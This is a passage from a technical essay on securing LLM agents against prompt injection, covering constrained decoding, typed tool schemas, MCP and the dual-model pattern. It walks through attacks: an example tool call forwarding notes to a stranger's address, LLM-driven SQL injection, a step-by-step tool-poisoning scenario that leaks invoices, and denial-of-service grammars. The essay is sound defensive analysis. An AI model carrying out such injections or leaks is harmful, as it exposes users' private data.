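1 − (1 − 0.0041)^200 ≈ 56%

Real attempts are not independent, because some scenarios are easier to attack than others and adaptive attackers learn from their failures. But an attacker who can keep trying needs only one success, so per-attempt success rates can make a model look much safer than it is.

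Anthropic also says that Claude Mythos 5, which shares its underlying model with Fable 5, achieved the best result so far on an external injection benchmark by Gray Swan. A review of the next system card, *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, reports a further improvement against indirect injection. Anthropic has since moved to version 5.2, which Mowshowitz (2026) reviewed in November in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*.

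Chen and colleagues found that OpenAI's GPT-5.5 was about as secure as their much smaller Qwen model under the adaptive AgentDojo attack. On DTaP, injections succeeded in 20.8% of cases against GPT-5.5 and 7.6% against the Qwen model. DTaP's developers reported 8.1% for Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. The three models ran in different agent software, which could account for some of the differences.

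A model can also achieve a low rate by refusing legitimate work. Claude Opus 5.0 completed 70.0% of the AgentDyn tasks with no attack present, compared with 83.3% for GPT-5.5 and 71.7% for the undefended Qwen model. Chen and colleagues inspected the failures and attributed much of the shortfall to excessive refusals.

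## Grammar-constrained tool calls

Training can make a model less likely to follow instructions in a stranger's email, but it can't rule this out. Developers can get a firmer guarantee about the model's output, because a tool call, unlike an email, has a useful grammar. Constrained decoding enforces that grammar as the model generates the call.

### Masking invalid tokens

Before the model generates anything, a program called a grammar engine translates the tool's schema into a grammar, and the grammar into an automaton that can read the output as it grows. Geng, Cooper and colleagues (2025), in *JSONSchemaBench*, set out the loop that follows:

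1. The engine updates the automaton with the output so far.
2. It computes a mask, which marks every token in the vocabulary as permitted or blocked. A token is permitted if the output could still grow into a valid string after it.
3. The model computes a probability for every token, as usual.
4. The decoder sets the probabilities of the blocked tokens to zero and rescales the others so that they add up to 1.
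5. It picks a token using the new probabilities and adds it to the output.
6. The loop repeats until the decoder picks the end token, which the mask permits only when the output is already a complete valid string.

Willard and Louf (2023), in *Efficient Guided Generation for Large Language Models*, illustrate masking with a decimal number and a vocabulary of five tokens: `A`, `.`, `42`, `.2` and `1`. At the start, the engine blocks only `A`. If the decoder picks `.2`, the number has its decimal point, so only `42`, `1` or the end token can follow. With some invented probabilities, the next step might look like this:

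| Next token | Model's probability | Probability after masking |
|---|---|---|
| `.` | 0.5 | 0 |
| `42` | 0.2 | 0.5 |
| `1` | 0.1 | 0.25 |
| End of output | 0.1 | 0.25 |
| `A` or `.2` | 0.1 | 0 |

The permitted tokens have a total probability of 0.4, so the decoder divides each of their probabilities by 0.4.

The same procedure limits the mail assistant to its three tools. When the output reaches the value of the `name` field, the mask permits only tokens that can begin `read_inbox`, `send_email` or `create_event`. The model can't call `delete_email`, however high a probability it gives that name.

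For a finite automaton, *Automata-Based Steering of Large Language Models for Diverse Structured Generation* (2025) defines the permitted tokens in state *q* as

*V*valid(*q*) = {*w* in *V* : δ*(*q*, *w*) is in *Q*live}

Here *V* is the vocabulary, δ*(*q*, *w*) is the state that the automaton reaches from *q* by reading all the characters of token *w*, and *Q*live contains the states from which it can still reach an accepting state. Current vocabularies often contain more than 100,000 tokens, so testing every token at each step would be slow. Willard and Louf therefore compute the set once for each state, before generation begins, and store the results in an index. Each step then needs only a lookup, and the average lookup time does not depend on the size of the vocabulary.

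### Tokens that straddle grammar symbols

An automaton that reads single characters can process a token such as `.2`, which combines a decimal point and a digit, one character at a time. Larger grammars make such tokens harder to handle, because parsing in practice usually has two stages. A lexer groups characters into symbols, such as a string, a comma or a closing bracket, and a parser then checks the order of the symbols. The model's tokens often don't begin and end where these symbols do. A token might be half a word from the body of an email, or it might be `","`, which ends one string and starts the next.

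Whether such a token is valid depends on the earlier output. At the end of the `subject` value, it is valid if the call still needs a body. If the call already has all three of its fields, the engine must block the token, because the schema forbids a fourth field.

Park, Zhou and D'Antoni (2025), in *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding*, explain the problem with a tiny language. The symbol B is an a followed by b's, and the symbol C is an a followed by c's. A valid string alternates between them: BC, BCBC and so on. Suppose the vocabulary includes the token `aba`:

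- At the start of the output, `aba` is valid, because `ab` is a B and the last `a` can begin a C.
- After `aba`, the engine must block `b`, because the unfinished symbol would become a second B.
- If the output so far is `ab`, the engine must block `aba`, because `ababa` also puts one B directly after another.

Their tool, GreatGramma, builds a table listing, for each lexer state and token, every sequence of symbols the token could produce. During generation, it uses the parser to check which of these sequences are acceptable and permits the matching tokens. Willard and Louf's earlier method also tracks partly finished symbols. In their Python example, the output so far is `def f`, and the `f` could be a whole function name or the start of a longer one. The token `oo(` is valid because it completes the name `foo` and adds the opening bracket that must come next.

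Engines differ in how much of this work they do in advance. Park and colleagues compared three of them on simplified grammars for Go, Java and Python. Outlines, the library that implements Willard and Louf's method, prepared each grammar in under five seconds but took 3 to 15 seconds per token. SynCode took 9 to 54 minutes to prepare a grammar and about 50 to 70 milliseconds per token. GreatGramma took at most about four minutes to prepare a grammar and 5 to 32 milliseconds per token. Tool schemas are usually much smaller than programming language grammars, but an agent may receive new ones with every request, which makes slow preparation a problem for tool calls too.

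XGrammar, a widely used engine, accepts or rejects most tokens in advance for each state of its automaton, without using the parser's stack. It checks the rest during generation. For example, a token made of two closing brackets is valid only if at least two brackets are open, and only the stack records how many are open.

*XGrammar-2* (Li, Dong and colleagues, 2026) adapts this design to agents. Its engine lets the model write free text until a tag opens a tool call. If the tag names `send_email`, the engine switches to the grammar for that tool's arguments, then returns to free text when the arguments are complete. The engine also saves parts of earlier grammars for reuse. In a test where each request had 500 tools drawn at random from a pool of 1,908, it could never reuse a whole grammar but could reuse 95.6% of the parts. On a dataset of realistic function calls, XGrammar-2 prepared a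 grammar in about 10 milliseconds, compared with more than a second for the original XGrammar. XGrammar-2 slowed the complete system by at most 6%.

For ordinary tool schemas, speed is no longer a good reason to leave the output unconstrained. LLGuidance, an engine from Microsoft Research, computes a mask for 128,000 tokens in about 50 microseconds. It arranges the vocabulary as a tree, so it can check a prefix once for all the tokens that share it. According to Guidance, the project LLGuidance is part of, the engine needs its full parser in only 0.1% to 1% of cases.

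### Asking for JSON and retrying

A developer could also simply ask for JSON. In the typical approach that Von Hippel and Miyazono describe, the developer prompts the model to return only an object that matches the schema, and the application then tries to parse the reply. The prompt doesn't guarantee that the reply will match. If the application converts replies carelessly, one that lacks a field may become an object with an undefined value, which later code uses. Von Hippel and Miyazono warn that OpenAI's JSON mode doesn't guarantee a match with the requested structure either.

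An application can also run a recognizer on the finished reply and generate a new one if the reply fails. Any reply that passes is guaranteed to be in the language, just as with constrained decoding. The simplest version, rejection sampling, sends the same prompt each time and discards the failures. If a fraction *p* of replies are valid, this takes 1/*p* attempts on average, which may be far too many for a long output with a strict grammar. According to *Constrained Sampling for Language Models Should Be Easy* (2025), this inefficiency led researchers to constrained decoding.

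One advantage of rejection sampling is that, unlike constrained decoding, it preserves the relative probabilities of valid replies. If one valid reply is twice as likely as another when the model runs freely, it is still twice as likely after the application discards the invalid ones.

### How masking distorts the output

Suppose a model's first token is `a` with probability 0.9 and `b` with probability 0.1. If the model then continues without constraints, it reaches a valid ending 1% of the time after `a` and 90% of the time after `b`.

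| First token | Probability | Chance of a valid ending | Probability of both |
|---|---|---|---|
| a | 0.9 | 0.01 | 0.009 |
| b | 0.1 | 0.9 | 0.09 |

Valid outputs have a total probability of 0.099, and those that begin with `a` account for 0.009 of it, or about 9%. About 9% of the outputs accepted by rejection sampling would therefore begin with `a`, and each valid output would take roughly ten attempts.

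Masking produces the token *a* 90% of the time. Both *a* and the other token can lead to a valid string, so the mask permits both and doesn't change their probabilities. If the decoder picks *a*, later masks force the output into an ending that the model would hardly ever have chosen. *Approximately Aligned Decoding* (2024) describes the fault as committing to a beginning even when its most likely continuations are errors.

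Park, Wang and colleagues (2024), in *Grammar-Aligned Decoding*, give the rule that would avoid this. If *x* is the output so far and *t* a possible next token, the decoder should pick *t* with a probability proportional to

*P*(*t* | *x*) × *c*(*xt*)

where *P*(*t* | *x*) is the model's ordinary probability for *t*, and *c*(*xt*) is the chance that the model would produce a valid string if it continued freely from there. Masking in effect replaces *c* with 1 wherever it is greater than 0. Computing *c* exactly is intractable in general. A parser can break a string into parts and analyse them separately, but the model's probability for each token depends on all the tokens before it.

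Park and colleagues demonstrated the effect by asking Mixtral-8x7B for a binary string that ends in 1. Without constraints, it succeeded about 90% of the time. They then imposed a grammar that allows `00000` and any five-digit string starting with 1. The success rate dropped to 30%, because the model often started with 0, after which the grammar allowed only `00000`.

Several methods approximate the correct rule. Park and colleagues' method, ASAp, samples repeatedly and lowers its estimate of *c* for beginnings that often lead to ungrammatical output. In *The Parser Already Knows*, Özgü, Wu and colleagues (2026) instead train a small model to estimate *c* from the candidate token and the lexer and parser states, which the grammar engine has already computed. On average, the KL divergence between this method's output distribution and the correct one was a quarter to a fifth of that for masking.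 The method took at most 1.25 times as long as masking, while ASAp took up to 20 times as long.

A distorted value can have the right format and still be wrong. Geng and colleagues imagine a model that is about to answer "89,000" in a field that permits only digits. The mask blocks the comma after "89", and the model might then write "890000". If the field were the amount in a payment tool, the result would be a well-formed call for a payment ten times too large.

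Experiments have produced conflicting results on how masking affects ordinary accuracy. Geng and colleagues tested Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct on three reasoning tasks, and all four open engines matched or improved on its unconstrained scores. The best one gained three to four percentage points. *STAGE* (2026), which covers turning source texts into JSON, found that constraints reduced the accuracy of Qwen3-4B's values from 69.1% to 66.9%. Some of the loss in such cases may come from the mismatch between tokens and grammar symbols. *Guiding LLMs The Right Way* (2024) found that accuracy can fall significantly when a decoder handles this mismatch badly, and proposed an algorithm that intervenes as little as possible. Researchers have also found that output constraints can weaken a model's refusals.

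### What the decoder guarantees

If the engine works correctly and the output is complete, the output belongs to the language of the grammar the engine enforced. Either condition can fail, and that grammar may not match the developer's schema.

Applications usually limit the number of tokens a model may generate, and Willard and Louf's algorithm includes such a limit. The mask ensures that a valid ending is always possible, but it can't ensure that the model reaches one in time. The `body` of an email may be any length, so the model could still be in the middle of it when the loop stops:

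```
{"name": "send_email", "input": {"to": "dana@example.com",
"subject": "Thursday", "body": "Two o'clock suits
```

A strict parser rejects this, but a tolerant one that added the missing quotation mark and brackets would send Dana half a sentence. This risk is a good argument for LangSec's revision of Postel's rule.

Matching the grammar to the schema is harder. Developers write these declarations in JSON Schema, which has many features, and engines support different parts of it. Geng and colleagues say that an engine truly covers a schema if its grammar permits every output that satisfies the schema and no others. Determining whether the engine's version of the schema matches its official meaning is the equivalence problem from LangSec. A schema may permit infinitely many outputs, so testing can't establish true coverage. Geng and colleagues instead measured whether the engine accepted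 the schema at all and whether the output then satisfied it.

The table shows the share of schemas that passed each test in two of their collections, one of function calls and one of long schemas with 100 to 500 fields.

| System | Function calls: accepted | Function calls: output valid | Long schemas: accepted | Long schemas: output valid |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No constraint | 100% | 90% | 100% | 13% |
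| Guidance | 98% | 96% | 60% | 41% |
| llama.cpp | 98% | 95% | 61% | 39% |
| Outlines | 99% | 95% | 47% | 3% |
| XGrammar | 100% | 93% | 69% | 28% |
| OpenAI | 89% | 89% | 9% | 9% |
| Gemini | 86% | 86% | Below 1% | Below 1% |

The open engines all ran with the same small model, Llama-3.2-1B-Instruct, so their results aren't directly comparable with those for OpenAI and Gemini. Some failures were timeouts, especially for Outlines. For function calls, even this small model produced valid output 90% of the time without constraints, and constraints added only a few percentage points. They helped much more with the long schemas.

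Geng and colleagues also ran the open engines on the official test suite for JSON Schema, which supplies valid and invalid examples for 45 categories of features. XGrammar let through at least one invalid example in 38 categories, but failed to compile schemas in only three. Guidance let through invalid examples in just one category and had compilation errors in 25. From a LangSec point of view, Guidance's errors are much safer. A developer notices when an engine rejects a schema, but may never notice that it has silently dropped one of the schema's requirements. (Several of the benchmark's creators work at Microsoft, where Guidance comes from, although the test suite itself is independent.)

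These results date from January 2025, and the engines have improved since, but the problem remained in June 2026. In *STAGE*'s experiments, XGrammar compiled 798 of 851 schemas. On those 798, Qwen3-4B's constrained outputs satisfied the schema 95.2% of the time, compared with 92.1% without constraints. Only 0.2% of the constrained outputs failed to parse as JSON, so truncation can't explain most of the remaining failures. XGrammar was probably enforcing a looser grammar than the schemas required. An application can catch such errors by checking the finished call against the schema with a separate validator before running it.

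Designers may also loosen enforcement on purpose, because the model may satisfy the missing requirements without being forced to. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (2026) studies the relationship between the language a model tends to produce, the one the task requires and the one the decoder enforces. When the enforced language fits the task, constraints help small models more than large ones.

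Commercial providers offer constrained decoding as a service. In August 2024, OpenAI introduced Structured Outputs, which constrains replies to a developer's JSON schema. According to Guidance, OpenAI had switched the feature to LLGuidance by May 2025, which let it handle a wider range of schemas. In earlier tests by Geng and colleagues, OpenAI and Gemini rejected most complicated schemas but usually followed the ones they accepted. OpenAI's outputs satisfied every accepted schema for function calls and 92% of the accepted schemas in a collection of medium-length ones.

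Tool calls may get this protection only in OpenAI's strict mode, and even there the promise concerns only the form of the call.

### Flaws in grammar engines

A grammar engine is supposed to protect other software from malformed data, but it also has to parse the schema or grammar it compiles, which an attacker may have written. GitLab's *CVE-2025-57809* (2025), an entry in a database of software vulnerabilities, notes that several tools pass their users' grammars straight to XGrammar. The entry concerns grammars with infinite recursion, which could make a service unavailable.

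Two more flaws in XGrammar followed. OSV's *CVE-2025-58446* (2025) describes a new optimizer that processed very large grammars so slowly that an attacker could tie up a model provider's servers. OSV's *CVE-2026-25048* (2026) describes a crash caused by deeply nested grammars, with a severity score of 8.7 out of 10. XGrammar's developers fixed the first flaw in version 0.1.24 and the second in version 0.1.32. Red Hat's *CVE-2026-25048* lists no workaround for the crash that meets the company's standards, so affected users need to upgrade.

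OSV rates both flaws as affecting availability but not the confidentiality or integrity of data. An attacker could therefore stop the service, but nothing suggests that the flaws would let invalid tool calls through. They are still awkward for a LangSec defence, because the engine apparently lacked adequate limits on the size, nesting and recursion of its own input. An agent that compiles schemas from a third-party Model Context Protocol server may expose its engine to the same kind of attack.

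Engines can also compute the wrong mask. When Park and colleagues compared GreatGramma with other engines, they found that SynCode blocked valid tokens in the Go grammar. They left XGrammar out of the timings because it couldn't compile their Java grammar and crashed or ran forever on the other two. All engines should produce identical masks for the same grammar and vocabulary, so a disagreement between two is a parser differential and shows that at least one is wrong.

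### A valid call that nobody wanted

With a tight schema and a correct engine, constrained decoding removes several kinds of faulty call:

- calls with broken JSON
- calls to tools that don't exist
- calls with missing or extra fields
- calls with values of the wrong type

This matters a great deal for reliability. Li and colleagues tested four Llama models on BFCL-v3, a benchmark of function calls, with and without XGrammar-2:

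| Model | Valid against the schema, unconstrained | Correct calls, unconstrained | Valid against the schema, constrained | Correct calls, constrained |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama-3.2-1B | 22.1% | 6.1% | 100% | 32.8% |
| Llama-3.2-3B | 40.7% | 33.1% | 100% | 77.8% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 67.0% | 59.5% | 100% | 80.9% |
| Llama-3.1-70B | 51.9% | 45.6% | 100% | 86.4% |

With constraints, the 3B model made more correct calls than the 70B model did without them. Every constrained call satisfied its schema, but the 70B model still got about 14% of its calls wrong, and the smallest model about 67%. Nobody was attacking the models, so these were ordinary mistakes.

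The security benefit is narrower. Constrained decoding makes it harder for an attacker to reach a bug in the parser behind the model, the danger von Hippel and Miyazono emphasize. Blocking invented tools adds less, because an application has no function to run for a tool that doesn't exist. Most of the attacks on the mail assistant in earlier sections use `send_email`, which the assistant is supposed to have, and don't need a malformed call or an invented tool.

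Suppose a stranger's email persuades the model to forward the user's confidential notes. The resulting call might be:

```json
{
  "name": "send_email",
  "input": {
    "to": "stranger@example.net",
    "subject": "Notes",
    "body": "Here are the notes from Monday's meeting."
  }
}
```

This call has the same three string fields as the reply to Dana, so the engine permits every token in it. The engine computes each mask only from the grammar and the output so far, without using the inbox or the user's request. An injection can therefore raise the probability of the stranger's address, and the mask will not lower it, because the schema accepts any string in the `to` field.

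## Typed tool schemas and the text they leave free

Developers can write much tighter schemas than the one for `send_email`, and the `to` field shows how much they gain by it.

### Three schemas for a recipient

So far the mail assistant has had the loosest declaration:

```json
"to": {"type": "string"}
```

The developer could add a pattern, written as a regular expression (a compact notation for a regular language), that accepts only strings shaped roughly like an address:

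```json
"to": {"type": "string", "pattern": "^[^@ ]+@[^@ ]+$"}
```

An enumeration, which lists every permitted value, could instead restrict the field to the user's contacts:

```json
"to": {"enum": ["dana@example.com", "lee@example.com"]}
```

| Proposed recipient | Any string | Address pattern | Contacts only |
|---|---|---|---|
| "Dana", without an address | Accepted | Rejected | Rejected |
| Dana's address | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted |
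| The stranger's address | Accepted | Accepted | Rejected |
| A new customer whom the user wants to answer | Accepted | Accepted | Rejected |
| Lee, a contact who shouldn't see the notes | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted |

The pattern catches mistakes such as a missing address, but it accepts the stranger's address, which is valid. Only the contact list blocks the call that would forward the user's notes to the stranger. The list is a finite language, so constrained decoding can enforce it whatever the stranger's email contains. But the list also stops the assistant from answering a new customer, and the application has to rebuild the schema whenever the contacts change. If the mail program automatically adds everyone who writes to the user, a stranger can get onto the list by sending an email.

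All three schemas leave `body` as free text. Even with the contact list in place, an injection could lead the assistant to send the notes to Lee, or to ask Lee in the user's name to approve a payment. The developer could cap the length, but a short message is enough for either purpose. Software can check recipients against a list, but a list of permitted bodies would limit the assistant to canned replies.

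Even the address pattern is easy to get wrong. A JSON Schema pattern may match any part of a string unless the developer anchors it to the start and end, as Wright, Andrews and Hutton (2022) note in *JSON Schema Validation*, the specification for these keywords. A developer who writes `@example\.com` to keep mail inside the company therefore also permits `dana@example.com.example.net`, which belongs to a different domain. JSON Schema also has an `email` format, but validators must leave this check off by default. Even when it is on, a validator may accept every string unless the schema's dialect makes format checks compulsory.

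The specification also permits null characters in strings, whether or not the receiving program can handle them. A validator may therefore approve a value that a tool written in C then cuts short at the null character. The PayPal certificate deceived browsers in the same way.

### Ranges, combinations and checks across fields

Suppose the developer extends `create_event` with a few more fields. The table shows some requirements the developer might have, and whether JSON Schema can express each one.

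| Requirement | JSON Schema |
|---|---|
| The title is a string of at most 100 characters | `type`, `maxLength` |
| The event lasts from 15 to 240 minutes | `minimum`, `maximum` |
| There are at most ten attendees, with no repeats | `maxItems`, `uniqueItems` |
| A call that gives an end time also gives a start time | `dependentRequired` |
| An online event has a link | `if` and `then` |
| The end time is later than the start time | No general way |
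| The date is not in the past | No general way |

Most of these keywords compare a value with a constant in the schema or check that a field is present. JSON Schema has no keyword for comparing the values of two named fields, and a schema has no access to today's date.

The `uniqueItems` keyword is an exception, because it compares the elements of a list with each other. It can take a schema outside the deterministic context-free languages, the class that LangSec recommends, even though a programmer can check for repeats with a few lines of code. For example, a schema can require a list of exactly two different strings. If a deterministic stack machine could recognize these lists, another could recognize the lists whose two strings are equal, because the deterministic context-free languages are closed under complement. But no stack machine can do that for strings of unlimited length.

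The last two rows of the table require a refinement, which is a type combined with a condition on its values. Von Hippel and Miyazono suggest that the contracts for structured outputs could include arbitrary predicates, meaning programs that return true or false. Such a predicate could compare the two times or look up the date. The check may depend on the whole call, so it is simplest to run it after the model has finished the call and before the tool acts. In an example from the Model Context Protocol documentation, a travel tool rejects a departure date in the past and returns an error message with the current date, so the model can correct the call and try again.

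No general procedure can determine whether two arbitrary predicates accept the same calls, or whether a given predicate always finishes. A developer who uses them gains precision but loses the guarantees that LangSec gets from simple grammars, so it makes sense to keep each predicate small.

JSON Schema has also become harder to process. *Validation of Modern JSON Schema* (Attouche, Baazizi and colleagues, 2023) gave the first formal description of its recent versions. The official text had allowed several reasonable interpretations of the new features, and this kind of ambiguity leads to parser differentials. The paper also showed that validation became PSPACE-complete in the 2020-12 version, so every known method takes exponential time in the worst case. Earlier versions could be validated in polynomial time.

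The cause is dynamic references, a feature that lets one schema redefine part of another schema it uses. If the schema is fixed, validation time is still polynomial in the size of the message. Developers who write their own tool schemas can therefore avoid the problem, but an agent that accepts schemas from other people's servers may still encounter it.

### A second language inside a string

A string argument can contain a whole program. One example in the Model Context Protocol is a tool called `execute_sql`, which takes two arguments, `region` and `query`. Both are strings, so the schema accepts any SQL command. Constrained decoding can keep the query from breaking out of its JSON string, but the database parses the contents of that string with a different grammar. JSON Schema has keywords for documents embedded in strings, but according to Wright and colleagues they are only annotations,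 so a validator doesn't use them to reject anything.

Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023), in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*, studied what happens when an application runs such queries unchecked. They built a job-posting website with a chatbot, using LangChain, a popular library for connecting models to other software. The chatbot answered questions in four steps:

1. A user asks a question, such as which jobs in London pay best.
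2. The model writes an SQL query.
3. LangChain runs the query on the site's database.
4. The model writes an answer based on the results.

The chatbot's database connection could read and change everything. Pedro and colleagues tried seven attacks on GPT-3.5, 30 times each. All of them worked every time, except one, which succeeded in 60% of runs against a version of the chatbot that could make several queries. Some attacks succeeded even though the prompt told the model not to change data, or to read only the current user's data. In others, an attacker used an ordinary web form to store text in the database, and the attack took effect when somebody else asked a question.

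These models are now very old, and current ones are harder to mislead. But whatever the model, an application built this way runs any SQL that the model writes.

Unlike in ordinary SQL injection, an attacker here can ask for the contents of a table in plain English, and the model writes the SQL. The query then need not contain any of the attacker's words, so Su and Wassermann's markers, described earlier, would have nothing to enclose.

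A recognizer for the safe sublanguage of SQL that von Hippel and Miyazono recommend could block commands that delete tables. It would do less to protect private data, because a query for user 6's email address has the same structure as a query for user 5's. The recognizer would also need the identity of the user making the request.

Pedro and colleagues tested four defences. A read-only database connection and a program that rewrites the model's queries both limit what a query can do, rather than how the model writes it. If user 5 is logged in, for example, the program replaces the users table in each query with a subquery that returns only user 5's record. The third defence loads the user's own data into the prompt in advance, so that the chatbot doesn't have to query for it. In the fourth, a second model inspects the query results for injections before the first model receives them.

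| What the attack did | Read-only connection | Query rewriting | Data loaded in advance | Second model |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Deleted or changed data at the attacker's direct request | Stopped | | | |
| Read other users' data | | Stopped | Stopped | |
| Changed data through stored text | Stopped | | | Stopped |
| Made the chatbot give a false answer through stored text | | | | Stopped |

In the last row's attack, the chatbot runs a permitted query for job postings, but text in the results leads it to give the next user a false answer. Controls on SQL can't prevent this because the answer is free text, like the body of an email. Only the second model caught the attack, and Pedro and colleagues concede that injections could mislead that model too. They reused the same seven attacks for this test, so the results don't show how well the defences would work against an attacker who adapts to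 them.

A narrower tool avoids much of the problem. Instead of `execute_sql`, the developer could offer `find_jobs`, which takes a city and a maximum number of results from 1 to 20, and put those values into a fixed parameterised query. Poll recommends less expressive interfaces like this one. But the chatbot could then no longer answer questions that the developer hadn't foreseen, and answering those is often the reason for using a language model.

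Other string arguments carry the same risk. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) traces similar paths from a prompt through a model into web pages, page templates and operating-system commands. It concludes that the model usually doesn't create the vulnerability but carries the attacker's influence to a component that already handled its input unsafely. Checking the string first is not always reliable, because programs that check shell commands have sometimes interpreted a command differently from the programs that run it.

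### What the Model Context Protocol types

Many agents get their tool schemas through the Model Context Protocol. Its current revision appeared on July 28, when its main software kits had a reported total of close to half a billion downloads a month (Model Context Protocol, 2026).

The revision makes tool schemas considerably more expressive. *Tools inputSchema & outputSchema Conform to JSON Schema 2020-12* (McBride and Hungerford, 2026) explains that the top level of an argument schema could previously contain only a type, the fields and a list of required fields. A server could restrict a single field, for example by listing its allowed values, but had no standard way to express conditions on the call as a whole. Servers may now use any JSON Schema 2020-12 keyword, so a search tool can require either an ID or a name, but not both.

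The 2020-12 version also made validation PSPACE-complete, and a malicious server could send a schema that is very slow to process. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) therefore recommends limiting the depth of a schema, the number of its parts or the time spent on each validation. A time limit would also curb slow validation caused by dynamic references. The rules also forbid software from automatically fetching parts of a schema from the network. LangSec researchers would probably approve of the rule that software should reject a schema if part of it is missing for this reason, instead of treating the missing part as permission for anything.

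Tool results can also have optional schemas. A server that declares one must return data that conforms to it, and the client (the application that calls the tool) should check that it does. For `read_inbox`, the schema could require a list of messages, each with a sender, a date, a subject and a body. An ordinary program could then sort the messages by date without guessing at the format. But the body, which contains the injection, is still a string. The protocol also recommends returning the same data as plain text for older clients.

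A typed argument may also identify something without giving the caller the right to use it. A shopping server might give the model a basket number to repeat in later calls. The documentation calls such a number "a name, not a capability" if the server can identify the caller, so the server should check the caller's authorization on every call. In Hardy's terms, the schema can ensure that the deputy supplies a well-formed name, but it cannot grant authority over what is named.

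### Tool descriptions as a channel for instructions

The protocol leaves a tool's description as prose, which the model reads to decide when and how to call the tool. Servers can add annotations, which are yes-or-no hints such as whether a tool only reads data. But Model Context Protocol (2026) warned in March that an untrusted server can label a tool read-only and still delete the user's files. Clients must treat annotations as untrusted unless they trust the server, and should get any firm guarantees from network controls or sandboxing.

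Tool poisoning is an attack that puts instructions for the model into a tool's description. Microsoft credits Invariant Labs with first disclosing the technique in April 2025, and describes how it could work against a company's finance team:

1. The team builds an agent to help with invoices. It connects the agent to a database of approved vendors, to its email and to another company's server, which checks bank details.
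2. A developer of that server changes the tool's description but leaves its name and the summary that users see as they were. The new description tells the agent to summarise the last thirty unpaid invoices and include the summary in the call.
3. The team's software doesn't ask for new approval when a description changes, so the agent starts using the new one.
4. An analyst asks a routine question about a supplier. The agent collects the invoices and sends the summary as an extra argument.
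5. The server returns a plausible answer and passes the invoices to the attacker.

The agent stays within its permissions, since the analyst may read the invoices and the team has approved the server. A schema that forbids extra fields would reject the call in step 4 if the team had kept its own copy. But the server supplies both the schema and the description, so it could add the extra field to the schema in the same update.

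LangSec offers little help here because it protects the receiver of a message from the sender by letting the receiver define the language. In tool poisoning, the receiver is the attacker and defines a language that suits the attack. The sender needs its own rules about what may leave the company, and those rules concern the content of the call more than its form. Microsoft recommends reviewing every change to a tool description as strictly as a change to the system prompt. The protocol advises clients to show users the arguments of each call before sending it, which would give the analyst a chance to notice the invoices.

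### CBCL, a language for messages between agents

O'Connor objects that the Model Context Protocol's schemas are too permissive, and CBCL is a much stricter alternative. It is probably the most thorough application of LangSec to agents so far. Every message is a nested list in brackets, built on eight core message types that include `tell`, `ask` and `reply`:

`(tell @dana "Two o'clock suits me.")`

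Agents can extend this vocabulary by sending each other dialects. A dialect defines new message types through templates, which turn each new message into core ones. In O'Connor's logistics example, a `track-shipment` message with a package number and a route becomes a `tell` message to a tracking service. The definition of a dialect is itself a CBCL message, so agents don't need a second parser for it. Before installing a dialect, an agent checks it against three rules:

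- **R1:** No template may refer to itself, either directly or through other templates.
- **R2:** The dialect must declare limits on its use of resources. These can't exceed 64 levels of nesting, 8,192 characters of expanded text and one second of checking.
- **R3:** The dialect may not redefine any of the eight core types.

These rules limit what templates can do, but they don't by themselves keep the language deterministic as it grows. Combining two deterministic context-free languages can produce one that is not deterministic, because the parser may need to apply one of the grammars before the input shows which is correct. CBCL avoids this by requiring every dialect message to begin with the word `lang` and the name of the dialect, so the parser can switch to the right grammar before reading the rest. As long as no two dialects have the same name, an agent can install any number of them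 and the combined language stays deterministic.

O'Connor proved this in Lean, a language in which a computer checks every step of a proof. The 176 theorems also show that the parser always finishes and accepts exactly the messages in the formal grammar. O'Connor extracted a working parser from the proofs and tested a faster version, written in Rust, against it. The Rust version has good test coverage but no proof of its own. It handles a simple message in less than 400 nanoseconds, so speed is not an obstacle.

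O'Connor acknowledges that CBCL can't constrain what a message means. A dialect's author can attach example messages with their expansions, and another agent can check that its own software expands them the same way, but the two agents may still understand the result differently. Templates also can't make one field depend on the content of another, add up the items in an invoice or check that a reply belongs to an earlier conversation. Tools and agents' actions are outside CBCL's scope. A dialect could define a `forward-notes` message that expands into an instruction to a mail server and still satisfy R1, R2 and R3.

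CBCL's parser never confuses instructions with data, and O'Connor claims that this addresses the parser-level weakness behind prompt injection. As an example of the danger, O'Connor cites ClawWorm, a self-spreading attack that succeeded 64.5% of the time against the agent framework OpenClaw, whose models couldn't distinguish their owner's instructions from other text. O'Connor's claim goes too far, because a `tell` message can contain any sentence in its quotation marks. If the receiving agent passes that sentence to a language model, it enters the same context window as the model's instructions, just as the body of an email would.

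## Typed values and fixed plans between untrusted text and action

Several research groups have tried to keep free text, such as the quoted sentences in CBCL messages, away from any model that calls tools. In their designs, a separate model that can't call tools reads the untrusted text. Ordinary software checks whatever passes between the two models, so structured output becomes a security boundary inside the agent.

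### The dual-model pattern

Simon Willison proposed the basic design, the dual-model pattern, in 2023. A privileged model takes the user's request, plans the work and calls tools. A quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. A third component, which Beurer-Kellner and colleagues call the orchestrator, is conventional software that runs both models and stores the results. Suppose the user asks the mail assistant to send Lee a summary of Dana's latest email:

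1. The privileged model asks for the email. The orchestrator fetches it, stores it as `$EMAIL` and gives the privileged model only that name.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$EMAIL`.
3. The orchestrator passes the email to the quarantined model and stores the reply as `$SUMMARY`.
4. The privileged model emits a `send_email` call with Lee's address and `$SUMMARY` as the body.
5. The orchestrator replaces the name with the text and sends the message.

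The privileged model's context contains the user's request and two variable names, but none of the email's text, so an instruction hidden in the email can't make the model call another tool or change Lee's address. This works much like a parameterised query.

The body of the message is still exposed, because an injection can make the quarantined model write anything in the summary. Beurer-Kellner et al. warn that a quarantined model with access to sensitive data might hide some of it in a draft, or add a new injection aimed at the user's colleagues.

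*Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* (Kim, Choi and Lee, 2025) distinguishes prompt injection from what it calls data injection, where the attacker supplies false information but no instructions. For example, a user asks an agent to find and follow a program's installation guide, and the agent finds one that an attacker wrote. The paper's system replaces untrusted data with identifiers, as in the dual-model pattern, and adds a check before such data can influence a privileged operation. On AgentDojo, the system scored 55.7% on the paper's measure of tasks completed securely, compared with 27.8% for an ordinary agent, and no attack against it succeeded.

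The dual-model pattern fails when the next step depends on the content of the untrusted text. For example, a privileged model that isn't allowed to read a bug report cannot determine which bug to fix.

### Four types that may cross

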